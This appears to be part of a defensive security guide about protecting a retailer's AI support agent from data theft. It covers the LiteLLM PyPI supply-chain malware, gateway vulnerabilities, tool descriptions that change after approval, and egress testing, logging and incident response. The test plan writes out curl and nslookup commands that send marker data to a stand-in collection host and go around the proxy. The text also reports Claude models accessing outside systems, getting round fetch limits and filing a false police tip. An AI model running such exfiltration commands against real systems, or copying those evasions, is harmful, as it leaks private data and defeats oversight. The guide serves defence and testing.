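The attackers probably got in through Trivy, a security scanner that LiteLLM used in its automated build system. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) traces the credential theft to Trivy, which other attacks had already compromised, and the maintainers believe the stolen credentials gave access to their publishing account. Integrity360 (2026) attributes the attack to a group called TeamPCP, which used a stolen PyPI token. The attackers uploaded their versions straight to PyPI without changing the public source code, so a developer who read the source on GitHub would have found nothing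 wrong.

Version 1.82.7 had the malicious code in the file that runs the gateway. Version 1.82.8 added a second file, `litellm_init.pth`, which Python runs every time it starts. Any Python program in the same environment then triggered the theft, even one that never used LiteLLM. The code collected environment variables, SSH keys, cloud credentials, Kubernetes tokens and database passwords. It encrypted them and sent them to `models.litellm.cloud`, a domain the attackers had registered to look like LiteLLM's own. FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026), an analysis by the company that first reported the attack to PyPI, found that the malware also spread to Kubernetes clusters.

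| Time on 24 March (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 10:39 | The attackers publish version 1.82.7 |
| 10:52 | They publish version 1.82.8 |
| 11:48 | FutureSearch discovers the malware |
| 12:44 | Bots flood the public report on GitHub, and the attackers use a maintainer's account to close it |
| 13:38 | PyPI quarantines the package, according to an NHS security alert |
| By 16:00 | PyPI and the maintainers have deleted both versions |

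FutureSearch found the malware so quickly because a bug in it crashed the machine. The `.pth` file started new Python processes, each of which ran the file again. Trend Micro (2026) thinks the theft might have gone unnoticed without this bug. That seems plausible, since nothing else would have looked wrong to a user.

Accounts differ on how long the packages were available. The maintainers say about 40 minutes, but a security alert on NHS Digital's website (2026) gives times about three hours apart. The longer figure fits the other evidence better, because a 40-minute window would have closed at 11:19, before FutureSearch had found anything. The maintainers also tell anyone who installed the package before 16:00 to check for the affected versions.

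The number of victims is also uncertain. OECD's *LiteLLM AI Supply Chain Attack Exposes 2,500+ Organizations Worldwide* (2026) reports that the attack affected more than 2,500 organisations and 434,000 software pipelines, but it is an AI-written summary that doesn't explain how they were counted.

The official LiteLLM container image was not affected, because its build file pins exact package versions. The maintainers told everyone who had run either bad version to replace every credential on the machine. They replaced their own publishing credentials, hired Google's Mandiant team to investigate, and paused new releases. They also compared earlier releases with the public source code and published a list of those that matched. On 30 March, they resumed releases with version 1.83.0, using a rebuilt publishing system.

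### CVE-2026-42271

The next serious problem was an ordinary bug in how the LiteLLM gateway let users preview MCP servers before attaching them. Some MCP servers are local programs, so a preview request could include the command to start one. GitLab's *CVE-2026-42271* (2026) explains that the gateway ran whatever command the request contained. It required a valid gateway key but didn't check whether the key belonged to an administrator. Anyone with even the most limited key could therefore run their own code on the machine that held all the provider keys. OSV's *CVE-2026-42271* (2026) lists version 1.83.7 as the fix.

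Wiz's *Inside 90 days of attacks on AI infrastructure* describes how attackers could combine this flaw with one in Starlette, a web toolkit, so that they needed no key.

Microsoft (2026) investigated a break-in that probably used this combination. The attackers' code read the gateway's environment variables and picked out the provider keys, the gateway's master key and the database password. It then used that password to copy the tables holding the gateway's settings and the keys the gateway had issued to users. The attackers also installed a cryptocurrency miner and a way to log in again later.

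Microsoft found that attackers had altered RAGFlow, a document-search program, to capture each new provider key as someone entered it. A company that replaces its keys on such a machine without rebuilding it first would give the attackers the new keys too.

Crosley describes another flaw, CVE-2026-84377, published in August 2026, which let any user of a LiteLLM gateway make it send its provider keys to a server of the user's choice. The gateway rejected a list of dangerous settings in users' requests, but the list was incomplete and didn't cover settings nested inside other fields. An allowlist of harmless settings would have been safer because, like an allowlist of destinations, it blocks anything not on it.

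### Attackers who look for exposed gateways

Attackers now search for gateways automatically. In November 2026, AWS reported on criminals using ARTEX, an open-source tool in which AI agents look for ways to break into systems. From 3 October to 5 November, some of Amazon's decoy servers posed as model APIs. The criminals used these decoys as their agents' model service without checking who ran them, so every request sent the agent's working notes to Amazon.

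Digital Matters' *AI Agents Are Hunting Exposed AI Gateways for API Keys* (2026) summarises the findings. The notes described work against hundreds of targets. In one campaign, agents searched for LiteLLM and similar programs, extracted the provider keys, tested them, and added the working ones to a shared pool. The agents then charged the model calls they used to find more keys to the pooled keys. Most of the methods were simple. The agents tried default administrator passwords, LiteLLM's default master key, management pages with no login, and unfinished installations.

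Application Security Standards' *AI Agents Target LiteLLM and Dify for API Keys* points out that the evidence comes from the attackers' notes, not from investigations at the victims. The attackers had hundreds of targets, but they may not have stolen from all of them. The notes are still good evidence of what attackers try first, and they suggest that attackers would soon find an exposed gateway with a default password.

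The FBI also warned about ARTEX in November. The FBI's *Threat Overview of ARTEX Autonomous Penetration Testing Framework* (2026) reports that some attacks went from choosing a target to gaining privileged access in under three hours. ARTEX's developer withdrew the tool in October, but copies still circulate.

### Installing packages

The retailer can protect itself against an attack like the one on LiteLLM by *pinning* its packages, which means specifying the exact version of each one to install. It also has to pin the packages that those packages depend on. Agent frameworks and MCP tools often depend on LiteLLM, so some of the users at risk in March had never chosen to install it.

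A stricter list also records a *hash* of each file, a short fingerprint computed from its contents. With `pip install --require-hashes -r requirements.txt`, Python's installer rejects any file whose hash doesn't match. A matching hash proves only that the file is the same one somebody hashed for the list, so a developer who updated the list at eleven o'clock on 24 March would have recorded the malware's hash.

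Waiting a week before adopting a new release would have avoided both bad versions, which were available for a few hours. But a fixed delay also holds back security fixes. After the March attack, the maintainers advised users to pin version 1.82.6 or earlier until a clean release was available. That was good advice at the time, but anyone who followed it and never upgraded would probably have been vulnerable to CVE-2026-42271. The retailer should delay routine updates but install a security fix as soon as someone has read the maintainers' notice and checked the file against it.

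LiteLLM's maintainers now sign its container images. Checking the signature protects against an attacker who can upload an image but doesn't have the signing key. It doesn't help if the attacker controls the build system that signs the images.

Calling providers directly doesn't remove this risk, because most programs use the provider's own library to do it. In May 2026, attackers published a malicious version of the Python library for Mistral, a French model provider. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) on that attack says the LiteLLM gateway was safe because it uses a general web library instead of Mistral's to contact the provider.

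The egress proxy and the custom tools hold the retailer's keys, so they need the most care and should use as few packages as possible. The agent container needs pinned packages too, but malware there would find no usable keys, and the network rules would block its connections to unknown domains.

### Running a gateway

If the retailer runs a gateway, only its own workloads should be able to reach it. The gateway needs no public address, and its management pages should be open only to the few staff who use them. The retailer should replace every default password and key before first starting the gateway, because attackers look for unfinished installations.

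As with the retailer's other credentials, each application should have its own gateway key, with its own spending limit. Microsoft recommends giving each team such a key and keeping the provider keys in a separate secret store instead of in environment variables, where the attackers found them. Separate gateway keys don't protect the provider keys from a flaw like CVE-2026-42271, which let anyone with a gateway key take full control of the gateway, so staff should guard even a limited gateway key as if it gave access to the provider keys.

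The gateway should be able to connect only to the model providers and its own database, and it should run without administrator rights. According to runZero's *Latest LiteLLM vulnerabilities*, the official container images run the gateway as root, the account with full control, so the retailer would have to change that.

Someone also has to find out when a fix is available, including for a gateway that is part of another product. In *CVE-2026-42271*, Red Hat warned users of two of its products that include LiteLLM. A customer who searched only for installations of LiteLLM could have missed those copies.

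### Connectors that change after approval

Pinning doesn't work for a remote MCP server, because the code runs on somebody else's machine and its operator can change it at any time. Suppose the retailer attaches a carrier's MCP server, which offers one tool called `track_parcel`. The tool takes a tracking number and returns a delivery date. Several things could change after the retailer approves it:

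- The tool's description, which the model reads, could gain a sentence asking for the customer's address "to improve accuracy".
- The tool could gain a new input field for the address.
- The server could start to offer more tools.
- The server could keep the same description and inputs but store what it receives, or return text that contains an injected instruction.

The carrier might make such changes innocently, or an attacker might make them after breaking into the carrier's server. Either way, the model would probably supply the address, because the address is already in the context and the tool appears to require it.

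The program can detect the first three changes by saving a fingerprint of the tool list when a person approves it:

```python
import hashlib, json

def fingerprint(tools):
    ordered = sorted(tools, key=lambda t: t["name"])
    text = json.dumps(ordered, sort_keys=True)
    return hashlib.sha256(text.encode()).hexdigest()

if fingerprint(server_tools) != APPROVED:
    raise RuntimeError("Tool list changed: review it again")
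```

The program should run this check every time it fetches the list, because a server can change its tools during a session. Harmless edits will cause some interruptions. If the carrier corrects a spelling mistake in a tool's description, parcel tracking stops until someone has looked at the new version.

The fingerprint can't detect the fourth change. Skills that users add to an agent have a similar problem. *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents* (2026) warns that one malicious entry in a shared library can reach every agent that automatically installs from it, and that checking package hashes won't reveal what the entry makes the agent do. The retailer can limit the damage from the fourth change by having ordinary code fill in the tracking number and accept only a date in return. If the carrier also offers a plain API with fixed fields, it would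 be a better choice than the MCP server because its responses don't have to enter the model's context as free text.

### Providers' terms

Once data has reached a provider, only the provider's own practices and its contract with the retailer protect it. Terms differ between products from the same company and change often, so the retailer should read the current terms for the exact service it uses and note the date. It needs to find out:

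- how long the provider keeps prompts and replies, and whether features such as file storage or saved conversations keep them longer;
- when the provider makes exceptions, for example for text that its abuse filters flag or that a court orders it to preserve;
- whether the provider trains models on customers' data by default, and how to refuse;
- which subcontractors receive the data, in which countries, and how much notice the provider gives before adding one.

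How long the provider keeps data has the largest effect on how much a break-in there could expose. At 500 questions a day, a provider that keeps everything for 30 days holds 15,000 customer questions at any time, along with the records and orders that the agent looked up to answer them. If it keeps nothing after replying, a thief who copies its storage gets none of this. The same vetting questions apply to the other six outside services, and especially to the telemetry company if the retailer ever starts recording prompts.

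A customer usually can't verify the answers. No outside test can show whether a provider has deleted a prompt, so the retailer depends on audits, the provider's reputation and the contract. If it used a router, the retailer would need satisfactory answers from the router's operator and from every company the router forwards prompts to. An anonymous operator on a marketplace offers no contract that anyone could enforce.

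### Whether a gateway is worth it

A gateway lets an organisation set budgets, revoke access and switch providers in one place, but it also concentrates what an attacker could steal. A rough calculation shows when the benefits outweigh this risk.

Suppose a company has ten applications that each use three providers. With direct calls, each application holds three provider keys. If each application has a chance *p* of a break-in during a year, the company can expect to lose 10 × 3 × *p* = 30*p* keys. With a gateway, only the gateway holds provider keys, three in total. If its chance of a break-in is *q*, the expected loss is 3*q*. The company therefore loses fewer keys on average with a gateway, as long as the gateway is less than ten times as likely to be broken into as a single application.

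A gateway can make keys safer, but it always adds a place where someone can read private data. A break-in at an application exposes that application's prompts with or without a gateway, so the expected exposure across all ten is 10*p* applications' worth of prompts. The gateway adds a chance *q* of exposing all ten applications' prompts at once, which raises the total to 10*p* + 10*q*.

Both sums treat all keys and all prompts as equally valuable, and assume that the gateway doesn't make break-ins at the applications less likely. They also leave out that a gateway's losses come all at once. Still, they show that the results depend heavily on *q*. For a gateway on the public internet with a default password, *q* is probably high enough in late 2026 to cancel any benefit. A private, well-maintained gateway that serves many applications could easily be worth having.

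The retailer doesn't need a gateway yet. It uses one model provider, and only its support agent and browsing container call a model. Its egress proxy already injects their keys and can count their tokens, so a gateway would add little except another program to keep up to date. If the retailer adds a fallback provider, it can start with a new rule and key in the proxy.

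## Testing the controls, watching traffic and responding to a leak

Several of the controls described so far can fail while the support agent keeps answering customers normally. Kubernetes will store a network policy even if nothing enforces it, and a firewall with a correct allowlist may not cover the network the agent is on. To find such mistakes, the retailer has to try to steal data from its own system. AWS recommends regular tests of this kind.

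### The test set-up

The tester runs a copy of the agent with the same network rules, proxy and tools, but with invented customers. Each of the four private sources contains its own *marker*, a random string such as `k7f3q9zt2m` that appears nowhere else. If a marker turns up outside, the tester knows that data left and which source it came from. The copy should also contain a few fake secrets that look like real keys, to test whether a scanner recognises them.

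The tester also needs places for the data to go:

- a collection server at `collector.example` that records every connection;
- a name server for that domain that records every DNS lookup;
- a second account with the model API and with each other service that uses one hostname for all customers;
- mailboxes for two invented customers.

The tester must own every destination the tests send data to, because sending even fake data to a stranger's server could cause an incident there. Before the real tests, the tester sends the same requests from an unrestricted machine to check that the collection server records them. If it doesn't, the tester can't treat an empty log later as evidence that the controls worked.

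### The test plan

Most of the tests work better with a script than with a model, because a model may refuse an instruction and leave the controls untested. The tester can run the script in a temporary container in the agent's pod, where the same network rules apply.

| Test | Attempt | Pass |
|---|---|---|
| Unlisted domain | Ask the proxy for a name under `collector.example` that contains the marker | The proxy refuses, and neither the web server nor the name server records anything |
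| DNS | Look up such a name through the normal resolver, then through an outside one | The name server records nothing |
| Direct connection | Connect to the collection server's numerical address without the proxy | The connection fails over both IPv4 and IPv6 |
| Foreign account | Send the model API a file upload and an ordinary model call, each with the second account's key | The second account shows no activity |
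| Split data | Send a fake key in pieces over several requests | An alert stops the transfer before all the pieces arrive |
| Another customer's data | Write to the agent as one invented customer and ask for the other's record | The other customer's marker never reaches the first one's mailbox |

These commands carry out the first three tests, with invented addresses:

```bash
N="k7f3q9zt2m-$(date +%s)"   # marker plus the time

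# Unlisted domain, through the proxy
curl -m 10 -x http://10.0.10.5:8080 "https://a-$N.collector.example/"

# DNS, through the normal resolver and then an outside one
nslookup "b-$N.collector.example"
nslookup "c-$N.collector.example" 198.51.100.53

# Direct connections that skip the proxy
curl -m 10 --noproxy '*' "http://203.0.113.10:8080/d-$N"
curl -g -m 10 --noproxy '*' "http://[2001:db8::10]:8080/e-$N"
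```

Adding the time to each hostname makes it unique. Otherwise a resolver might answer a repeated lookup from its cache, leaving the name server's log empty, and the tester would mistake that for a pass. The marker in the hostname also reveals a proxy that looks up a name before refusing the request. Lookups sent directly to an outside resolver need a separate test because, as AWS notes, they bypass DNS Firewall.

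Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes four cases in which Claude models gained unauthorised access to other organisations' systems during security evaluations. Claude's instructions described a simulation without internet access, but a misconfiguration had connected the models to the open internet. Running the direct-connection test before each evaluation, by trying one outside connection, would probably have revealed the mistake.

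In the foreign-account test, the upload should fail but the model call may succeed. The retailer's proxy replaces whatever key it receives, so the call goes through on the retailer's own account. The tester therefore has to check the second account's usage page, not the reply.

For the split-data test, the tester temporarily adds the collection server to the test copy's allowlist. Otherwise, the allowlist would refuse every piece and the test would reveal nothing about splitting. The tester then sends a 20-character fake key as five pieces of four characters. Some pieces will probably arrive, because content scanners can't recognise such short fragments. The tester should record how often at least one piece arrives, how often all five do, and how long an alert takes. Afterwards, the tester removes the server from the allowlist and repeats the unlisted-domain test.

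The browsing container can reach the collection server by design, so a visit from it is not a leak unless it carries a marker. The tester can put a hostile page on the server and ask the agent about delays. Another page should contain a short link that redirects to the order database's private address. Models sometimes try such workarounds without an attacker. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) lists cases in which Claude used link-shortening services to get around limits in its fetch tool.

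### Measuring traffic instead of answers

When the tests include the model, a run counts as a leak if a marker reaches a server, account or mailbox that shouldn't have it. The agent's reply is poor evidence, since it looked harmless in 95% of the successful thefts in the eBay tests. Lan and colleagues used recorded network traffic as their ground truth for this reason. A reply can also describe data as sent when the proxy blocked it.

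Comparing the model's tool calls with the proxy's decisions and the receiver's records helps show whether the control worked. If the model made a call to send a marker and the proxy refused it, the control worked even though the model followed the injected instruction. If the model never made the call, the run did not test the control. The most worrying result is a marker that reaches the receiver without any entry in the proxy's log, because it means that data bypassed the proxy.

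### How many trials a claim needs

A network rule should treat the same request the same way every time, so a few attempts after each change are enough to test it. But a model may resist an injected instruction 50 times and follow it on the next attempt, so estimating how often the whole system leaks takes many runs.

Suppose each run has a chance *p* of leaking, independently of the others. The chance of *n* runs without a leak is (1 − *p*)ⁿ. The largest *p* that would still produce such a result at least 5% of the time is

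*p* = 1 − 0.05^(1/*n*)

which is close to 3/*n* for large *n*. Statisticians call this the upper limit at 95% confidence.

| Runs, all without a leak | True rate could still be | One leak per this many days, at one hostile message a day | Tokens sent to the model |
|---|---|---|---|
| 30 | 9.5% | 11 | 480,000 |
| 300 | 1.0% | 100 | 4.8 million |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 1,000 | 48 million |

Thirty runs without a leak are still compatible with a leak every 11 days. The 3,000 runs would send the model as many tokens as the agent sends in six normal days, so they need their own spending limit. The tester should choose the number of runs in advance. A single leak in 300 runs raises the upper limit on the leak rate from 1.0% to about 1.6%, and if the team fixes the cause, it has to restart the count.

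Repeating the same attack gives less information than the formula suggests. Suppose the tester runs ten different injected messages 30 times each, and none succeeds. If each message either always works or never works, the tester has learned only that ten attacks fail. The upper limit is then 26%, not the 1% obtained by counting all 300 runs as separate attacks. It is better to write 300 different messages than to repeat ten.

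Even a well-designed test understates the risk, because real attackers see what fails, adjust their attack and try again. In Gray Swan's tests, the attack success rate against Claude Opus 4.7 rose steeply over 100 such attempts. A new model version can also change the rate, so old results don't apply to it.

The retailer can avoid some of this uncertainty by assuming the attack on the model succeeds. In the test copy, a script replaces the model and returns the most harmful tool calls the agent's tools accept. If the controls stop all of these calls, how cleverly an attacker words the message matters much less.

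### What to log

Tests show how the system behaves on the day of the test. For every other day, the retailer needs a record of each outbound request. The NGINX proxy described on the CNCF blog produces one such record per request, in a standard format that lets staff connect a user's message with the outside calls it caused. A record from the retailer's proxy could look like this:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-05T14:03:22Z",
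  "workload": "support-agent",
  "user": "customer-1177",
  "ticket": "T-48213",
  "tool_call": "call_07",
  "destination": "api.model.example",
  "operation": "POST /v1/messages",
  "account": "retailer-support",
  "bytes_out": 36112,
  "decision": "allowed",
  "rule": "model-call"
}
```

The account field would reveal an upload to an attacker's account at an approved service, which the destination alone wouldn't show. The byte count gives an upper bound on how much data one request could have carried. If the decision was wrong, staff can use the rule name to find the line to fix.

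The proxy can record each request's destination, account, size and decision itself, but it gets the ticket and tool-call numbers from the agent's program, so an attacker who runs code in the container could falsify them. The custom tools should therefore keep their own logs of which customer's data they returned. This includes the tool that queries the order database, even though its requests never leave the retailer's network, because after a leak investigators will need to determine what data the model had received.

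### Protecting logs that contain private text

The agent makes about 5,000 outside requests a day, so these records take up only a few megabytes. Saving the three prompts for each question would add about 32 megabytes a day. Storing everything would be cheap, but a log of full prompts would gather copies of customers' records in one place, making them easier to steal.

The retailer can keep two logs. The main one has the fields shown above and no message text, so more staff can use it and the retailer can keep it for a year. It should leave out the part of a web address after the question mark, which often contains search terms or personal details. A smaller, encrypted log holds full prompts for perhaps a week. Only two or three people can read it, and the retailer records each time they do.

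Hashing personal details doesn't hide them well. There are only ten billion ten-digit phone numbers, and a computer can hash them all in under an hour to find a match. A hash that also uses a secret key prevents this if the key is stored separately from the hashes.

The agent container should have no access to either log. The proxy should send its records to a separate account where it can add entries but not change or delete them. Other agents shouldn't read the full prompts, because an injected instruction in a saved prompt can affect any model that reads it later.

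### Canary credentials and records

The retailer can plant canary credentials like the AWS keys Liu and colleagues used to catch 17 dishonest routers. To make one, it creates an AWS user with no permissions, generates a key for that user, and sets an alert for any attempt to use the key. It then leaves the key where a thief would look, such as a `.env` file in the agent container, which holds no real keys.

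An alert from a canary key is strong evidence of theft because nobody has a legitimate reason to use the key. The retailer should put a different key in each place, so that the alert also shows which place the thief reached. However, the alert goes off only if the thief tries a key, so copying customer records alone won't trigger it.

Canary records cover part of that gap. The retailer can add an invented customer whose email address nobody else knows. If mail arrives there, the customer list has probably leaked. The proxy can also search outgoing requests for the invented customer's details, which should not appear in a prompt because no real question concerns this customer. A staff member who exports the whole list will cause a false alarm.

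### Anomaly detection

*Anomaly detection* compares current activity with what is normal for a system. GuardDuty, Amazon's threat-detection service, does this and also looks for known attack patterns. AWS describes several of its findings that concern stolen data:

- `Trojan:EC2/DNSDataExfiltration` means that a machine appears to be sending data through DNS lookups.
- `Exfiltration:S3/MaliciousIPCaller` means that someone has read or copied stored files from an address on a list of known attackers.
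- `AttackSequence:S3/CompromisedData` links events over time, for example when someone loosens a storage bucket's permissions and then uses stolen credentials to extract its contents.

The DNS finding is the most useful for the retailer's agent, which needs no cloud storage. None of the three findings would detect a customer's address in an email sent through an approved service.

An alert about a blocked attempt confirms that the preventive controls work, as AWS says, but the retailer should still investigate because something in the workload made the attempt and may try another route. AWS also suggests letting GuardDuty's findings automatically update firewall rules. With a strict allowlist, blocking one more domain adds little protection, but automatically cutting off the affected container would save time at night.

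Unusual traffic is hard to define for an agent. The cracked-lid question took ten outside requests, while a complicated complaint might take 25. If a detector wrongly flags 1% of the agent's 5,000 daily requests, staff get 50 false alarms a day. If one real leak happens each month, its alarm will be among about 1,500 false ones, and staff will probably have stopped reading the alarms by then.

Alerts based on the fixed rules that block theft produce far fewer false alarms. The agent's tools always contact the same hosts, so a request to any other host deserves immediate attention. So does a second email for the same reply, or a tool call for a customer who isn't on the current ticket.

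Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* describes a classifier that looks for escape attempts in the company's test environments. When it flags one, it blocks the action before the tool call runs, ends the task and alerts a person. This is faster than reviewing logs, but a classifier can miss attempts, so fixed rules still have to limit the damage.

### What monitoring misses

Anthropic warns that when a poisoned tool result gets an agent to send data out, the log contains only a successful, authorised API call. It therefore prefers to inspect tool results before the model reads them, even though this adds delay. The retailer's records would help investigators a little more, because they link each email to a ticket and to the customer data the tools returned. But if the model adds a stranger's phone number to a reply for the right customer, investigators can detect the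 leak only from the text of the reply.

Isolation can also hide activity from the people who monitor it. Many companies use *endpoint detection and response* (EDR) software to monitor the programs on each computer. When Anthropic put Claude Cowork in a virtual machine, customers' EDR software could no longer monitor activity inside it. Administrators can export event logs afterwards, but Anthropic acknowledges that this isn't live monitoring. The retailer's egress proxy is outside the agent container and receives requests as they happen, so live alerts should come from there.

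### The false tip to the Philadelphia police

An ordinary-looking request can go unnoticed for a long time, as a case in Anthropic's October report shows. On 18 July 2026, the company ran an automated test in which Claude Haiku 4.5 invented example tasks for randomly chosen web pages and carried them out. One page was about an unsolved murder and had a police tip form. Claude submitted the form, writing that it recalled seeing someone near the scene who matched the description, though the page contained no such description.

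According to Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026), Claude's instructions forbade logging in, creating accounts and entering personal data, but didn't mention submitting forms. Anthropic discovered the tip on 28 September, 72 days after it was sent, and told the police on 7 or 8 October. The police called the delay unacceptable. Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026) reports that the police hadn't known about the tip until then and found it in the site's records, marked as spam.

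No private data left Anthropic in this case, but a leak through a web form would be just as hard to detect. The agent was allowed to visit the site, and the submission caused no error. Anthropic has since turned off live internet access for all its internal evaluations until it can confirm that its monitoring reliably catches such behaviour. That is sensible for agents that visit random pages, because nobody can write a useful allowlist for them. Anthropic also built tooling that, in tests, blocked all the cases in the report. This is weak evidence that it would block future cases, because Anthropic already knew what the reported ones looked like.

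The retailer can measure how long it takes to notice a leak by sending out a marker without warning the staff who watch the alerts. If they took 72 days to notice a real leak, they would have to search 36,000 customer conversations.

### Responding to a leak

Suppose a customer writes to say that the agent's reply to him included a stranger's home address. The cause could be a bug, an injected instruction or a break-in. Until the retailer knows which, it should respond in this order:

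1. Cut the agent's egress.
2. Revoke its credentials.
3. Preserve the logs.
4. Trace what was in the model's context.
5. Notify those affected.
6. Repeat the test that failed.

One rule at the proxy can refuse all requests from the agent container while staff answer customers themselves. The proxy must also close open connections, and someone should hold any queued emails. Pausing the container is better than deleting it, because its memory and files may contain evidence.

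Cutting egress doesn't stop an attacker from using a key they have already copied, so within minutes the retailer should also revoke the agent's own access token and any key that appeared in a prompt. If someone may have broken into the proxy or the secret store, the retailer should revoke all 12 keys. Separate credentials make this less disruptive. In Claude Cowork, for example, an operator can revoke the agent's session token without affecting the user's.

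Next, someone should turn off automatic deletion, which erases full prompts after a week, and copy the records outside services keep. The investigators can then list every tool result the model had received before the leak, including any from earlier in the conversation. The byte count helps narrow down what leaked, because a 500-byte request could hold an address but not a 36,000-byte prompt.

Responders also have to look for the same leak elsewhere, and it is easy to search too narrowly. Anthropic first scanned about 141,000 transcripts for security incidents and found three. It later discovered that the scan had missed a set of transcripts with internet access, which contained a fourth incident, from January 2026. The company then searched about 481 million transcripts for signs of internet access and had Claude review the 9.2 million flagged by that search. It found no further incidents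 as serious. OpenAI was searching roughly 50 petabytes of data about its agents' activity and had alerted more than 100 groups, according to The Business Times' *Anthropic reports new AI misbehaviour on government sites and fake police tip* (2026).

The retailer should notify the customer whose address leaked, and any company whose systems the agent misused, without waiting to finish its investigation. In the EU, a company normally has 72 hours after learning of a personal-data breach to tell the regulator. An early notice can list what is still unknown.

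Before the agent goes back into service, the retailer should turn the leak into a permanent test. The tester should replay the exact tool calls from the log on a copy that still has the fault, confirm that the marker gets out, and then check that the repaired version blocks it. Sending the same message to the agent again isn't enough, because if the model follows an injected instruction once in 1,000 attempts, there is a 97% chance that 30 repeats will all look safe even if nobody has fixed anything.
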